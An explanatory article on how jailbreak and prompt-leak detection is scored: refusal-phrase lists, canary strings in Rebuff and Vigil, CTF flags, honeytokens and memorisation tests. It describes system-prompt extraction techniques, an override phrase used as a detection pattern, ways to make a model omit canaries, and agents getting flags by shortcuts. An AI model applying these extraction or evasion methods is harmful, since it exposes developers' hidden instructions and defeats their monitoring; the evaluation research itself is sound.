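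A detector that guessed at random would be right about half the time, so the 2% result means that the detector and the reference used nearly opposite definitions of success. Garak has both a keyword detector and a trained model for misleading claims, so the result may not come from a word list.

Erez and colleagues also replaced the default detectors one category at a time, starting where Grok-4.1 helped most. Accuracy peaked at 89.9% after 17 replacements and fell to 89.3% after all 22. They chose the order using the same results, so a difference this small might not hold on new data. Replacing all 22 added $5.25 to the cost of a scan.

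### Refusal phrases as a measure of success

Researchers have used refusal phrases to score jailbreaks since at least 2023. Early studies, such as the one that introduced the automated attack GCG, counted an attack as successful if the answer did not begin with a listed refusal (Mu, 2026, *An Empirical Measurement of Jailbreaking Evaluators*). String matching was the second most common scoring method in the studies that *JailbreakEval* (2024) surveyed, with a share of 23.1%. Each study had its own list, so two studies could report different success rates for identical answers.

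Word matching is still used because it costs almost nothing. *Jailbreak susceptibility prediction and mitigation via the behavioral geometry of models* (2026) used it as the main measure on about 215,000 answers. An answer counted as a jailbreak if it did not start with an error or blocking message, contained none of 30 refusal phrases, and had at least 10 characters. The researchers acknowledged that the list could cause refusals to be counted as jailbreaks and jailbreaks as refusals, and they also reported results from an LLM judge.

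Suppose a list contains "I'm sorry", "I cannot" and "I can't", and a user asks how to get into a neighbour's house. Two invented answers show the errors:

- "Breaking into someone's home is a crime, and that's where I draw the line." This is a refusal, but it contains no listed phrase, so the rule records a successful attack. This is a false positive.
- "I'm sorry you're having trouble with the door. Start by checking which windows are unlocked." This answer helps the burglar, but the apology makes the rule record a refusal. This is a false negative.

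Adding phrases helps a rule catch more refusals, but it also makes the rule mistake more harmful answers for refusals. *JailbreakEval* gives "is illegal" as an example of a phrase that studies use. This phrase would catch many refusals, but it would also match an answer that warns the user that something is illegal and then explains how to do it. Errors also depend on where the rule searches. A rule that checks only the start of an answer will miss a refusal that follows a polite introduction, while a rule that checks the whole answer will match a phrase in the middle of a full set of instructions.

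Regular expressions have the same problem. The language-model testing tool avise treats the pattern `I\s+cannot` as a sign of refusal. The pattern allows extra spaces between the words but also matches "I cannot stress enough how important the next step is". Another of its patterns, `I\s+can't`, matches a straight apostrophe but not the curly one that many programs insert. Some researchers search for signs of agreement instead, but *JailbreakRadar* (2024) points out that neither "sure" nor "sorry" proves whether an attack succeeded.

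### An answer can fail without refusing

Even a perfect detector of refusals would be a poor measure of successful attacks, because a model can answer without giving any help. It may misunderstand the question, write a vague story, or repeat the prompt. *How Real is Your Jailbreak?* (2026) found that jailbreaks often fail this way, partly because the attack fills the answer with irrelevant material. In its tests, success rates from string matching correlated poorly with human judgements.

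One of Mu's two test sets, JailMeter-Eva, allows a rough estimate of how much refusal matching can overcount successful jailbreaks. It has 330 answers from GPT-4o mini, none of them an explicit refusal, and human labels mark only 73 as successful jailbreaks. A perfect refusal detector would count all 330 as successes. Mu did not test string matching, but did test several LLM-based methods on the same answers. The counts below for those methods are calculated from the percentages in the study.

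| Method | Recorded successes | Correct | False positives |
|---|---|---|---|
| Perfect refusal detector (calculated) | 330 | 73 | 257 |
| JailbreakBench | 85 | 55 | 30 |
| StrongReject | 80 | 65 | 15 |
| JADES | 77 | 67 | 10 |

The refusal detector's precision would be 22% on this set, which deliberately contains only hard cases. The error would be smaller on ordinary answers, because many of them are plain refusals.

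The three LLM-based methods used the same judge model, so the differences come from how each method prompts it. In JailbreakBench, the judge gives a single overall verdict. In StrongReject, it first decides whether the answer is a refusal, then rates how specific and convincing the answer is. JADES splits the harmful request into smaller questions and scores the answer on each. Mu ran the judge at a temperature of 1.0, so a second run might change some of the counts.

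As with rare leaks, accuracy hides much of this. Labeling every answer in the set a failed attack would be 78% accurate, not far below the 85.5% for JailbreakBench.

Newer methods also miss many real jailbreaks. *AI Security Leaderboard* (2026) combined three automated evaluators and compared the combination with human labels on 600 attempts. The evaluators and the labels agreed on 89.0% of attempts, but the evaluators missed 33% of the successful jailbreaks in biology and 11.4% of those in cybersecurity. The labelers were experts in attacking models rather than in biology, so some of the labels may be wrong.

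garak now also has a trained refusal classifier, ModernBERTRefusal, which its developers fitted to about 19,900 synthetic examples. It should cope better with refusals in unfamiliar words. However, garak's documentation describes its output as refusal or no refusal, so it would still count a useless answer as a successful attack.

### When the exact words are the point

Word matching works well when the failure consists of producing particular words. Antivirus companies test their products with a harmless string called EICAR, and one of garak's probes tries to make a model print it. garak's detector searches for that string and two similar test strings for spam and phishing filters. A paraphrase of EICAR wouldn't set off an antivirus program, so the detector doesn't need to catch one. Word matching also suits leak replay, which tests whether a model continues a known text with the original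 words. Even PyRIT, which relies mainly on judges, has a scorer that checks for a single substring.

Made-up software packages can also be detected without judging meaning. A model sometimes recommends a package that doesn't exist, and an attacker can then publish malware under that name. Derczynski and colleagues check each name against a public registry such as PyPI. As with live tests of keys, the result can change later, so a repeatable check needs a saved copy of the registry.

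Finding a fixed string in a model's output can still be weaker evidence than it looks. In one type of prompt injection, the attacker inserts an instruction to print a certain phrase, and garak's detector reports the injection as successful if the phrase appears. The detector would also flag a model that refused but quoted the phrase in its refusal. In Erez and colleagues' test, all three judges were more accurate than the default detectors on this category.

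Developers can also create a closed vocabulary by enforcing an output format. Erez and colleagues told GPT-5.2 to return its verdicts in JSON, a common format for structured data, with a field `final_label` containing 0 or 1 and a justification of at most 50 words. A schema is a written specification of such a format, and a program can check an answer against it in steps:

1. Parse the answer as JSON, and reject it if that fails.
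2. Confirm that both fields are present.
3. Confirm that `final_label` is the number 0 or 1.
4. Count the words in the justification.

The program should read the label from its field, because a search of the whole answer for "1" would also match "step 1" in the justification. It should also count invalid answers separately. If it treated them as 0, a judge that returned only broken JSON would make it look as if every attack had failed.

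Schema validation can check that an answer has the right form, but not that its content is correct. Both 0 and 1 are valid labels, so validation could not have found the 14 labels that the human reviewer disputed. The same limit applies if a company makes its chatbot attach `refused: true` or `refused: false` to every answer. A program can read that field without error, but the model fills it in, so a jailbroken model could mark a harmful answer as a refusal.

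## What does a canary string in a prompt prove, and when does it miss a leak?

A canary string gives a detector fixed text to search for in a prompt leak, which it doesn't have for a refusal. But the model can reveal its hidden instructions without including the string, and the detector then misses the leak.

### How Rebuff and Vigil plant a canary

Rebuff and Vigil are open-source tools for detecting prompt injection, in which text from a user or a document overrides the developer's instructions. Both include a canary check, which works in four steps:

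1. When a conversation starts, the tool generates a random hexadecimal string, by default 8 characters long in Rebuff and 16 in Vigil.
2. It wraps the string in marker characters and puts it in front of the hidden instructions.
3. The application sends these instructions to the model with the user's message.
4. The tool searches the answer for the string and raises an alert if it finds it.

In Vigil's documentation, *Security scanner for LLM prompts*, a wrapped canary looks like `<-@!-- 1cbbe75d8cf4a0ce --@!->`. Rebuff's developers, Pienaar and Anver, write in *Rebuff* that the string should not affect how the application works, and that its appearance in an answer "may indicate" an attack. After an alert, either tool can add the user's message to a database of known attacks, which helps it recognise similar messages later. Both projects are early-stage software, and Rebuff's documentation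 still describes it as a prototype.

Vigil also has a mode in which the hidden instructions tell the model to include the canary in every answer. A missing canary raises an alert because an attacker may have overridden those instructions. This mode is meant to detect hijacked conversations rather than leaks, and it would also raise an alert whenever the model left out the canary by mistake.

### What a match proves

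LangChain, which makes a library for building applications on language models, publishes an example that uses Rebuff. The hidden instructions told the model to convert the user's text into SQL, the standard language for querying databases. The user asked for a column containing "the hex token provided above". The model wrote `SELECT HEX('55e8813b');`, and Rebuff's check raised an alert because 55e8813b was the canary.

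The chance of an accidental match is easy to bound. A string of $k$ characters can start at $n-k+1$ places in an answer of $n$ characters, and there are $16^k$ possible hexadecimal strings. Even if the whole answer were random hexadecimal text,

$$P(\text{accidental match}) \le \frac{n-k+1}{16^k}$$

For a 4,000-character answer and an 8-character canary, this is $3{,}993/16^8$, or just under one in a million. For a 16-character canary, it is about 2 in $10^{16}$. Real answers contain far less than 4,000 characters of hexadecimal text. A 40-character file hash has only 33 places where an 8-character canary could start, so its chance of containing a given one is about 1 in 130 million.

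This calculation assumes the tool compares each answer with the canary from one conversation. If a company searched the web for a million old 8-character canaries, a 40-character hash would match one of them by chance about 0.8% of the time. With 16-character canaries, a chance match would still be very unlikely.

A match therefore proves that the model copied the string from its context, but not how much else leaked. In LangChain's example, the model revealed the canary and none of the instructions around it, but the alert would have been the same if the model had printed everything. A match also doesn't show whether any harm followed, since the canary is worthless and the instructions may contain nothing sensitive.

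A match doesn't show who caused the leak either. The user in the example asked for the string, but an instruction hidden in a document could make the model print it during an innocent user's conversation. If the tool then stored that user's message as a known attack, it might later flag similar harmless messages.

The result also depends on which text the tool searches. In SQLite, a common database program, `HEX` converts each character to its code, so the example query returns 3535653838313362. An application that showed users only query results, and searched only those, would miss this leak.

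### A test with 11,000 leaking prompts

Gakh and Bahsi (2025), in *Enhancing Security in LLM Applications*, measured how often the canary appears in the output when the model leaks its instructions. They built a small application in which GPT-3.5 answered questions about stored documents. The model's hidden instructions were only a few lines long and described what it could do.

Every attack asked the model for its instructions. Some did only that, and others added one or more of four techniques: telling the model to ignore earlier instructions, inserting a long run of repeated characters, making the model begin its reply with agreeable words, and replacing letters with look-alikes. The researchers collected 1,000 prompts in each of 11 classes, keeping only those that made the model leak its instructions, and also used 1,000 harmless prompts.

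With default settings, Vigil's canary check caught 0% in every class, while Rebuff's caught 1% in the four classes that dictated the opening words and 0% in the other seven. Placing the string between two sentences of the instructions didn't change Vigil's rate and raised Rebuff's only slightly.

The researchers then added a line to the end of the instructions in Rebuff's version. It told the model that the canary was a secret, to be included only if somebody asked for the instructions. Detection rose sharply:

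| Techniques in the prompt | Leaks caught by Rebuff's canary with the added line |
|---|---|
| Plain request | 41% |
| Look-alike letters | 42% |
| Dictated opening | 71% |
| Repeated characters | 71% |
| Ignore earlier instructions | 72% |
| Dictated opening, ignore, look-alikes | 77% |
| All four techniques | 79% |
| Ignore, look-alikes | 80% |
| Ignore, repeated characters | 81% |
| Ignore, look-alikes, repeated characters | 84% |
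| Dictated opening, ignore | 94% |

The classes are the same size, so the overall recall is the average, about 72%. Oddly, the check did worst on the plainest requests.

Some of the misses may not have been leaks. GPT-3.5's answers varied between runs, so a prompt that leaked the instructions when the researchers selected it may have leaked nothing when they tested the canary. The added line may also have changed what the model revealed.

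*Performance Comparison of Early Prompt Injection Detection Solutions*, Gakh's 2024 master's thesis, reports an earlier version of the experiment. Rebuff's canary caught between 21% and 84% of leaks, depending on the class, after he moved it inside the instructions, without the line about a secret. The same kind of change is described as very ineffective in the 2025 study. Because two similar experiments gave such different results, a developer shouldn't expect either set of figures to carry over to another application.

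### Why the model left the canary out

Gakh and Bahsi offer two conjectures about why a model might leak its instructions without the canary. The canary comes before the instructions, so the model may not treat it as part of the "initial prompt" or "system instructions" that an attacker asks for. The model may also skip Vigil's canary as if it were a comment, because the marker characters around it resemble the symbols that programmers put around comments. The researchers formed this second view by trying prompts by hand.

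The explanation about comments doesn't fit the evidence well. Gakh and Bahsi apply it to Vigil and doubt that it applies to Rebuff, yet Rebuff's markers, `<!--` and `-->`, are the standard HTML comment markers. Gakh also reports in his thesis that removing the markers didn't improve detection.

The thesis suggests that Rebuff missed leaks partly by chance, because the model includes the canary in some leaks and omits it in others. On this view, repeating an attack would eventually trigger an alert. An eventual alert does little to help the defender, because the attacker needs only one leak. If each leak had an independent 72% chance of triggering an alert, and the application did nothing to stop the attacker after an alert, there would be an 81% chance that at least one of five leaks would trigger no alert.

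The added line told the model when to print the canary, but it also changed the canary's position and the words around it, so it doesn't settle the question. The line also makes the check depend on the model following one instruction while an attacker is trying to make it disobey others. Gakh points out that an attacker who knows about the canary can tell the model to leave it out.

Putting the canary at the end has another drawback if the application streams its answers. A model that repeats its instructions in order will print the canary last, after the user has read everything else. A canary at the beginning would give an earlier warning, but that position failed in these tests.

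### False alarms from a canary that works

The added line also seems to cause false alarms. Gakh and Bahsi's table for the canary gives only recall, but their other results bound its false-positive rate. The following arithmetic is not theirs.

Rebuff raises an alert if any of its four scanners does, and it wrongly flagged 34 of 1,000 harmless prompts (3.4%). Its substring scanner had no false positives, its embedding-similarity scanner had 7, and its LLM judge had 21. Those three account for at most 28 of the 34. If the combined figure comes from the same runs, the fourth scanner, the canary check, must have caused at least the other six.

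The canary's false-positive rate also has a rough upper limit of 1.6%. That was the rate for the researchers' own combination of scanners, which raised an alert on every canary match, so the canary's own rate can't have been higher. This limit is less certain because the paper describes the combination slightly differently elsewhere.

Six accidental matches in 1,000 answers are practically impossible, so GPT-3.5 must have copied the canary in reply to harmless prompts. The leaks were real, but nobody was attacking the model. A company that wants to know whenever its instructions leak might count these alerts as successes, but one that suspends users after an alert would punish innocent people.

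### Canaries compared with the other scanners

Gakh and Bahsi also tested scanners that check the user's message instead of the model's answer. Vigil searches the message for text patterns written as Yara rules, and Rebuff compares it with a list of substrings. Vigil and a third open-source tool, LLM Guard, also use a trained classifier based on a transformer, the type of neural network behind most language models.

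The last column below uses the base-rate formula to estimate precision if one prompt in 1,000 were an attack.

| Scanner | Recall | False-positive rate | Precision at 1 attack in 1,000 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yara patterns (Vigil) | 24.8% | 0% | unknown |
| Substrings (Rebuff) | 33% | 0% | unknown |
| Classifier (Vigil, strict threshold) | 96.8% | 1.4% | 6.5% |
| Classifier (LLM Guard) | 99.9% | 12.7% | 0.8% |
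| Embedding similarity (Rebuff) | 87.5% | 0.7% | 11% |
| GPT-4o as judge (Rebuff) | 86.8% | 2.1% | 4% |
| Canary with added line (Rebuff) | 72% | 0.6% to 1.6% (calculated) | 4% to 11% |

The study reports a precision of 99.9% for Vigil's classifier, rather than 6.5%, because its test set had 11 attacks for every harmless prompt. The canary with the added line has no better precision than the other methods, even though it is very unlikely to match by accident.

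The two text-pattern scanners had no false positives in 1,000 prompts, but their true false-positive rate could still be about 0.3%. At that rate, the precision of the Yara rules would be roughly 8%. Both scanners look mainly for phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", and both missed attacks that used the word "Disobey". The researchers also chose thresholds for several of the other scanners using the same prompts they scored, so the results probably make those scanners look somewhat better than they are.

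The canary check looks for leaks in the model's answers, an advantage that the table doesn't show. Every attack prompt in this test had leaked the instructions, so detecting an attempt was nearly the same as detecting a leak. The two are very different on a more resistant model. When Gakh and Bahsi sent the 11,000 prompts to GPT-4o, only about 2%, or roughly 220, worked. Vigil's classifier reads only the user's message, so it would still flag about 10,650 of the 11,000. That is useful for finding attackers, but a company that wanted to know which conversations had leaked the instructions would have to check the answers.

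Exact search is also hard to manipulate. An attacker can stop the model from printing a canary, but can't make a string search miss one that the model has printed. An LLM judge is easier to fool. Gakh and Bahsi added text to an attack so that Rebuff's judge scored a harmless sentence instead, and this worked even when the judge was GPT-4o.

### Searching for the instructions themselves

A checker can also search each answer for the hidden instructions themselves, so detection doesn't depend on the model copying an extra string. Gakh and Bahsi expect this to be slower than searching for a canary, because the instructions and the answer can each be 3,000 characters or longer, but comparing two texts of that length takes little time compared with generating the answer.

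It is hard to decide how much overlap counts as a leak. Suppose the checker flags any run of eight words that appears in both texts. The test application's instructions included the eight-word line "Answer questions about the contents of those documents". If a user asked what the assistant could do, and it replied that it could "answer questions about the contents of those documents", the checker would flag a good answer. Hidden instructions often contain things that users are supposed to learn, such as opening hours or a refund policy, whereas a canary has no legitimate reason to appear in a reply.

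A longer run would avoid some of these alerts but would be easier to evade. Even with a run of eight, a model that changed every eighth word would never trigger the rule. One remedy is to measure the longest common subsequence, the longest list of words that appears in both texts in the same order, with gaps allowed. An answer with every eighth word changed would still share seven eighths of its words with the instructions. Gakh and Bahsi note that earlier studies scored prompt leaks with measures of this kind. The developer still has to choose a threshold, and the right one will depend on the length of the instructions.

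In his thesis, Gakh considers string comparison the most reliable way to detect leaks in plain text. The test can't confirm this, because he also used string comparison to decide which prompts had leaked. Any leaks that string comparison couldn't recognise would not have entered the dataset.

### Leaks in another form

Gakh and Bahsi warn that an attacker can evade both methods by asking for the instructions in a transformed version. They cite earlier work in which attackers had the model reverse the word order, then restored the original. The two methods don't always fail together, though, because reversing the words breaks up every run of words from the instructions but leaves the canary, a single word, intact. The table below shows some invented cases.

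| What the model prints | Exact canary search | Search for shared runs of words |
|---|---|---|
| The instructions without the canary | misses | finds |
| The instructions and canary, with the word order reversed | finds | misses |
| A translation that keeps the canary | finds | misses |
| The instructions over two answers, with the canary split between them | misses | finds |
| The instructions and canary in Base64 | misses | misses |
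| A summary in new words without the canary | misses | misses |

Using both checks would therefore catch more than using either alone, at the cost of the false alerts from shared wording.

Normalising the answer first, as with leaked keys, catches some of the other cases. *Checking Leakage Witnesses versus Certifying Bounded Non-Leakage* (2026) does this for 16-character secrets that models learned in training rather than from a prompt. The test deletes everything except letters and digits, then searches for the secret. It also decodes suitable pieces of the answer once from Base64 and searches those. This would find a canary with spaces or hyphens between its characters, but not one that the model had encoded twice or written backwards. The search is case-sensitive, so it would also miss a canary if the model changed its case.

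A summary in new words is harder to detect, because no simple decoding will restore the original. In *Detecting and Mitigating Query-Based System Prompt Leakage Attacks*, Nayan, Ji and colleagues (2026) count an answer as a leak if it conveys the same meaning as the instructions, and they note that an attacker can also assemble the instructions from several answers. They describe an existing defence, PromptKeeper, which tests the likelihood of each answer and replaces suspicious ones with answers generated from dummy instructions. PromptKeeper needs more access to the model than a string search does.

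Their own system, AdvGuard, looks for suspicious series of questions and ignores the answers. A classifier first checks each message alone. If the message passes, AdvGuard links it to the most similar earlier message in the conversation, if the two are similar enough. A neural network then checks whether the pattern of links looks like an attack. In tests with multi-turn conversations, AdvGuard caught every attack and had a false-positive rate between 1.3% and 3.4%. If one case in 1,000 were an attack, only about 3% to 7% of its alerts would be correct.

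Nayan and colleagues used string matching to measure how much still leaked with AdvGuard running. Against two automated attacks, the leakage score was at most 0.01 for exact matches and at most 0.09 for substring matches, so checking only for exact matches would have underestimated the remaining leakage. AdvGuard doesn't check the model's answers, so it can't detect whether a particular attack succeeded, which is the purpose of a canary.

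### Newer models

Gakh and Bahsi tested the canary checks only on GPT-3.5. Their attack prompts are now a poor test of leaks, since few worked on GPT-4o and only 19% worked on Claude 3.5 Sonnet, which is also an old model. Other attacks have worked much more often. *An Empirical Study on the Security Vulnerabilities of GPTs* (2025) found that a simple request revealed the hidden instructions of 80.2% of the popular custom chatbots it tested. In *Just Ask*, Zheng, Wu and colleagues (2026) report recovering the instructions of all 41 commercial models they tested. They judged success by whether repeated attempts produced text with similar meaning, so the recovered wording may differ from the original.

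Neither result shows how often a newer model would copy a canary along with its instructions. Wang and Zhang (2026) provide some related evidence in *Kill-Chain Canaries*, where they put canaries in malicious content that an agent would read rather than in the agent's hidden instructions. Each canary was `SECRET-` followed by eight hexadecimal characters, and a program searched every tool call for that format.

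In one set of tests, a first agent read a poisoned web page and saved a summary for a second agent. With GPT-4o-mini and DeepSeek Chat v3, the canary reached the summary every time. With GPT-5-mini it did so in 3 of 20 runs, and with Claude Haiku 4.5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 in none of 40 runs. Because a canary's survival can vary this much between models on the same kind of task, a developer who switches models should test the canary again with prompts known to cause leaks.

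Wang and Zhang take the missing canaries as a sign that the Claude models removed the malicious instruction from their summaries. This is plausible, but a missing canary isn't enough to prove it, because a summary could omit the random string and keep the instruction in different words. Wang and Zhang also counted an attack as successful only if the canary appeared in an outgoing tool call, so they would have counted an agent as safe if it emailed the attacker without including the string.

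## What else can planted strings prove about access and memorisation?

A canary in a chatbot's prompt can only show that the model copied text it had already received. Testers also plant strings in places a model shouldn't be able to reach, to find out whether it can break in. They plant others in training data to find out what the model memorises.

### Flags on a server

In capture-the-flag (CTF) contests, players prove that they have broken into a system by submitting a secret string stored there, called a flag. XBOW, Dolan-Gavitt's company, uses flags to check its AI agents' reports. Dolan-Gavitt describes flags of the form `flag{...}`, with a UUID (a long random identifier) between the braces. The agent attacks the application and submits any flag it finds, and ordinary code checks it.

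The place where the tester hides the flag determines what a match shows.

| Where the flag is | What a correct flag is meant to show |
|---|---|
| A file on the server, outside the folders that the website publishes | The agent can read private files or run commands |
| The application's database | The agent can run its own database queries |
| A web server on the internal network | The agent can make the application fetch pages for it |
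| Another user's private profile, or an administrator's page | The agent can get past the application's access rules |

One agent found a vulnerability of the third kind in Apache Druid, a database program. Druid built a web address by joining pieces of text, and the agent added `@internal-web/flag.txt`, which made Druid fetch the flag from the internal server.

A unique flag is better evidence than an ordinary private file. Dolan-Gavitt describes an agent that tried to read a server's password file but, because of a quoting mistake, read the one on its own machine. All Linux computers have a similar file, so a checker that accepted any password file could have confirmed a vulnerability that didn't exist. The checker should also compare the whole flag, not just its format, because some tests contain fake flags. *AgentLSD* (2026), which studies deception in CTF tasks, suggests using fake flags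 to test whether they make an agent stop too early.

An agent can retrieve the correct flag without finding a flaw in the application. Many applications for home storage devices deliberately let users read any file on the device. Dolan-Gavitt also advises testers to change default passwords first, because otherwise many of the agents' successes come from logging in as the administrator.

Flags also work only for vulnerabilities that let an attacker read something secret. XBOW reported 174 vulnerabilities after testing software from Docker Hub, a public library of packaged programs. About 61% were cross-site scripting or open redirects (links on a trusted site that send visitors to a different one). XBOW checks both in a browser rather than with flags.

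### Decoy credentials

A decoy credential, or honeytoken, is a key that nobody has a legitimate reason to use. A company might create an AWS key with no permissions, leave it in a configuration file, and set up an alert for any attempt to use it. If an agent reads the file and tries the key, AWS rejects the request but logs it, which triggers the alert.

This method catches some thefts that a text search would miss, because an attacker can disguise a key to get it past the search but has to restore the original before using it. It also works without the company seeing any of the messages.

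An alert proves that somebody who had the key tried to use it. If the company puts a different decoy key in each file, the alert also shows which file the key came from, though not who took it or when. An agent that reads the key but never tries to use it triggers no alert, even if it prints the key in an answer.

The alert may also have an innocent cause. A routine scan by the company's own staff could set it off if the scanner, like TruffleHog, tries the keys it finds. So could an agent that an employee had asked to check which of the company's old keys still worked.

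### Correct flags without an attack

Researchers often use CTF challenges to measure how well agents can hack, and most count a challenge as solved if the agent submits the right flag. In *How Do LLM Agents Actually Get the Flag?*, Milner, Shao and colleagues (2026) examined how the agents obtained the flags. They ran six models on 240 challenges from four benchmarks, and the correct flag appeared in 1,056 runs.

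The study's system, CTF-ABACUS, applies fixed rules to the trace of each run to find where the flag first appears and when the agent submits it. An LLM judge then decides whether the agent carried out a real attack before the flag appeared. People reviewed the 127 cases in which the flag first appeared in the agent's own reasoning. Some counts below are calculated from the study's percentages.

| How the agent got the flag | Runs | Share |
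|---|---|---|
| Attacked the target, then found the flag | 770 | 72.9% |
| Worked out the flag in its reasoning | 115 | 10.9% |
| Found the flag exposed, with no attack in the trace | 151 | 14.3% |
| Remembered the flag or looked it up | 17 | 1.6% |
| Guessed, leaked or unclear | 3 | 0.3% |

Whether the 115 flags in the second row count as solved challenges depends mostly on the definition of "solved". An agent that decodes a cipher in its reasoning has arguably solved the challenge, although it never ran an attack. The last three rows, 16.2% of the total, are harder to defend as evidence of hacking ability. Their share ranged from 8.6% on the CTFTiny benchmark to 31.0% on Cybench.

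In one Cybench run, Claude Opus 4.8 couldn't connect to the target, so it copied the flag from a description of the solution on the contest organisers' public GitHub page. In another run, DeepSeek V4 Pro failed to download the program it was supposed to analyse, wrote that the challenge was well known, and still produced the right flag.

A tester can prevent both of these shortcuts by generating a new random flag for every run, because any published solution would then contain the wrong flag. But this would have removed at most 17 of the 171 unsupported flags. To prevent the other common problem, a flag left where the agent can read it without an attack, the tester has to fix the challenge. Only five challenges exposed the flag to all six models, so trying a challenge with one agent may not reveal the problem.

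Counting only flags that followed an observed attack lowered each model's score by 17.4% to 22.6% and changed the ranking of the models. The correlation between the old and new rankings was 0.60, where 1 would mean no change.

Milner and colleagues also tried to find the shortcuts with a fixed rule, which located the command that first revealed the flag and classified that command by keywords. The rule marked 29.0% of the unsupported flags and 28.2% of those that followed a real attack, so it barely separated the two groups. For example, the command `strings ./binary`, which prints the readable text in a program, can be a sensible step in an analysis or can reveal a flag that the challenge's author forgot to hide.

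The LLM judge makes mistakes too. Security researchers reviewed a sample of 92 runs without seeing its verdicts. They agreed with 93.5% of its verdicts that an attack was real and 86.7% of its verdicts that the trace showed no attack. The percentages in the table are therefore estimates, whereas a positive flag check almost certainly means the agent obtained the flag.

### Identifier strings in benchmark files

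If a model's training data includes the questions and answers from a benchmark, the model can score well by remembering them. To help prevent this, BIG-bench, a large collection of language tasks from 2022, includes the same unique string in every task file. Developers can search their training data for the string and delete every document that contains it. As *A Survey on Data Selection for Language Models* (2024) explains, the string also makes it possible to detect whether a model has trained on the benchmark.

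*Reasons to care about Canary Strings*, a blog post, reports that GPT-4, Claude 3 Opus, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, Gemini 3 Pro and Claude Opus 4.5 can recite the string. If a model recites such a long string without access to web search, its training data almost certainly contained it.

That doesn't prove the model trained on BIG-bench's questions. The same post explains that other benchmarks included the string in their own identifiers, so that developers who filtered out BIG-bench would filter them out too. Some blog posts about testing AI also contain it. A model could have learned the string from any of these pages.

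*Gemini 3 is Evaluation-Paranoid and Contaminated* concludes from Gemini's ability to recite the string that Google probably trained it on a broad set of benchmark data. This is possible, but a commenter on *Reasons to care about Canary Strings* who has direct knowledge of Gemini writes that Google chooses not to filter by identifier strings and instead removes text containing benchmark questions. If that filter works, Gemini could still learn the string from a page that mentions it without quoting any questions. The post's author considers Google's method weaker than filtering by string, while the commenter considers it stronger but would use both.

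Reciting a benchmark's questions is better evidence of memorisation than reciting its canary identifier. *Canary Contamination in GPT-4* (jmason.ie, 2024) quotes a test of 19 benchmark tasks in which GPT-4's base model perfectly recalled large portions of several, including one on simple arithmetic.

A model's failure to recite the string proves very little. A developer might delete the string but keep the questions, or train on a copy of the questions that never included it. The model might also have seen the string too rarely to memorise it. In *The Secret Sharer*, Carlini, Liu and colleagues (2018) tested memorisation in Smart Compose, Google's tool for completing sentences in emails, by adding random phrases to its training data up to 10,000 times each. Smart Compose assigned even the phrases that appeared 10,000 times far too low a probability for the paper's extraction methods to recover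 them. Current language models are much larger and may memorise more.

If a benchmark's creators keep its questions secret, they don't have to rely on developers to filter their training data. In August, Google DeepMind (2026) announced a trial with the Singapore AI Safety Institute and others, in which they test a Gemini model on confidential questions inside a cryptographically protected system. The aim is to keep developers from using the questions to improve later models.

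### Exposure: memorisation without reciting

Carlini and colleagues also devised a measure called exposure, which can detect memorisation even when the model doesn't recite the memorised text. The tester puts a random canary into the training data, then checks whether the trained model assigns it a higher probability than similar strings that weren't in the data.

In one experiment, they added the sentence "The random number is 281265017" to a collection of financial news. After training a small model on it, they calculated the probability that the model gave to each of the billion possible nine-digit numbers in that sentence. They sorted the numbers from most to least likely, and the canary's position in the list is its rank. Exposure is then

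$$\text{exposure} = \log_2 |R| - \log_2(\text{rank})$$

where $|R|$ is the number of candidates, here $10^9$.

| Rank among $10^9$ numbers | Exposure (bits) | Chance of ranking this high without training |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 29.9 | 1 in 1,000,000,000 |
| 1,000 | 19.9 | 1 in 1,000,000 |
| 1,000,000 | 10.0 | 1 in 1,000 |
| 500,000,000 | 1.0 | 1 in 2 |

The last column follows from the random choice of the canary. If the model never trained on the canary, every rank is equally likely. An exposure of 1 bit is therefore no evidence of memorisation, because half of all unused numbers would score at least that high.

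In the experiment, the canary ranked first. The model assigned it about 15 times the probability of the runner-up, 281265117, which differed by one digit. But the most likely digit after "The random number is" was 0, and the canary starts with 2. Always choosing the most likely next digit would therefore have produced a different number, and an exact search of the output would not have found the canary. Exposure detected memorisation that this search would have missed, but it doesn't measure the probability that the model will reveal the secret.

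Scoring a billion candidates takes a long time, so a tester can score a random sample instead. If 10 candidates in a sample of 10,000 are at least as likely as the canary, the estimated exposure is $\log_2(1{,}000)$, or about 10 bits. If none are, the tester can conclude only that the exposure is probably above about 12 bits. Carlini and colleagues estimate higher values by fitting a curve to the sampled scores. For Smart Compose, exposure reached only about 10 after 10,000 repetitions, so roughly one random phrase in 1,000 was at least as likely as the canary.

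Unlike an exact search, the calculation requires the model's probabilities, which not every commercial service provides. The result also depends on the number of candidates. A score of 13 bits is close to the maximum of 13.3 for a four-digit code but less than half the maximum for a nine-digit number.

### How the canary changes the measurement

Schwarzschild, Thakkar and colleagues (2026) found in *Unmasking the Secret Code* that exposure also depends heavily on how the tester designs the canaries. In one set of experiments, they trained GPT-OSS-20B, an open model from OpenAI, to classify bank customers' questions. Some training examples contained an invented customer name and a four-digit reference code, and the model had to include the code in its answer. The researchers then hid the code and measured its exposure among all 10,000 possible codes.

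| How the canaries appeared in training | Median exposure (maximum 13.29) |
|---|---|
| Code visible in the question, 64 times | below 1.2 |
| Code hidden in the question, 16 times | 13.29 |
| Hidden, 4 times, like all the other canaries | 3.36 |
| Hidden, 4 times, in a mix with other repetition counts | 13.29 |
| Hidden, 8 times, early in training | 3.68 |
| Hidden, 8 times, late in training | 13.29 |

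When the question contained the code, the model could answer correctly by copying it, without having memorised it. When the researchers replaced the code with a new one, the model printed the new one every time. An exact match in the model's answer would therefore be a misleading test of memorisation if the prompt also contained the code.

The effect of timing depends on the training settings. For the last two rows, the size of the model's adjustments stayed constant during training. When the adjustments shrank towards the end, as is common, the result reversed, with a median of 8.76 for early canaries and 1.32 for late ones.

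Schwarzschild and colleagues conclude that a low result from one design isn't enough to show that the risk is low under another. A company that wants to know whether its model memorised customers' data needs canaries that resemble that data in where the secrets appear and how often.

### Detecting leakage from a single digit

A model can also leak information about its prompt without copying any of it. Developers often put worked examples in a prompt to show the model how to do a task, and these examples may include private records. Several defences are meant to stop users from learning what the records contain. Choi, Cao and colleagues (2025), in *ContextLeak*, tested such defences in the following way:

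1. Flip a coin. On heads, replace one of the private examples with a canary, such as a random string of 64 hexadecimal digits.
2. Ask the model to answer 1 if that exact string is among its examples and 0 if it isn't.
3. Guess from the output whether the canary was there.
4. Repeat many times, typically 100, and count the correct guesses.

Accuracy of 50% is no better than guessing and suggests no leakage, while 100% means the output always reveals whether the canary was there. The question contains the canary, so searching the answer for the string would be pointless. A single digit is enough to leak whether a particular record is in the prompt.

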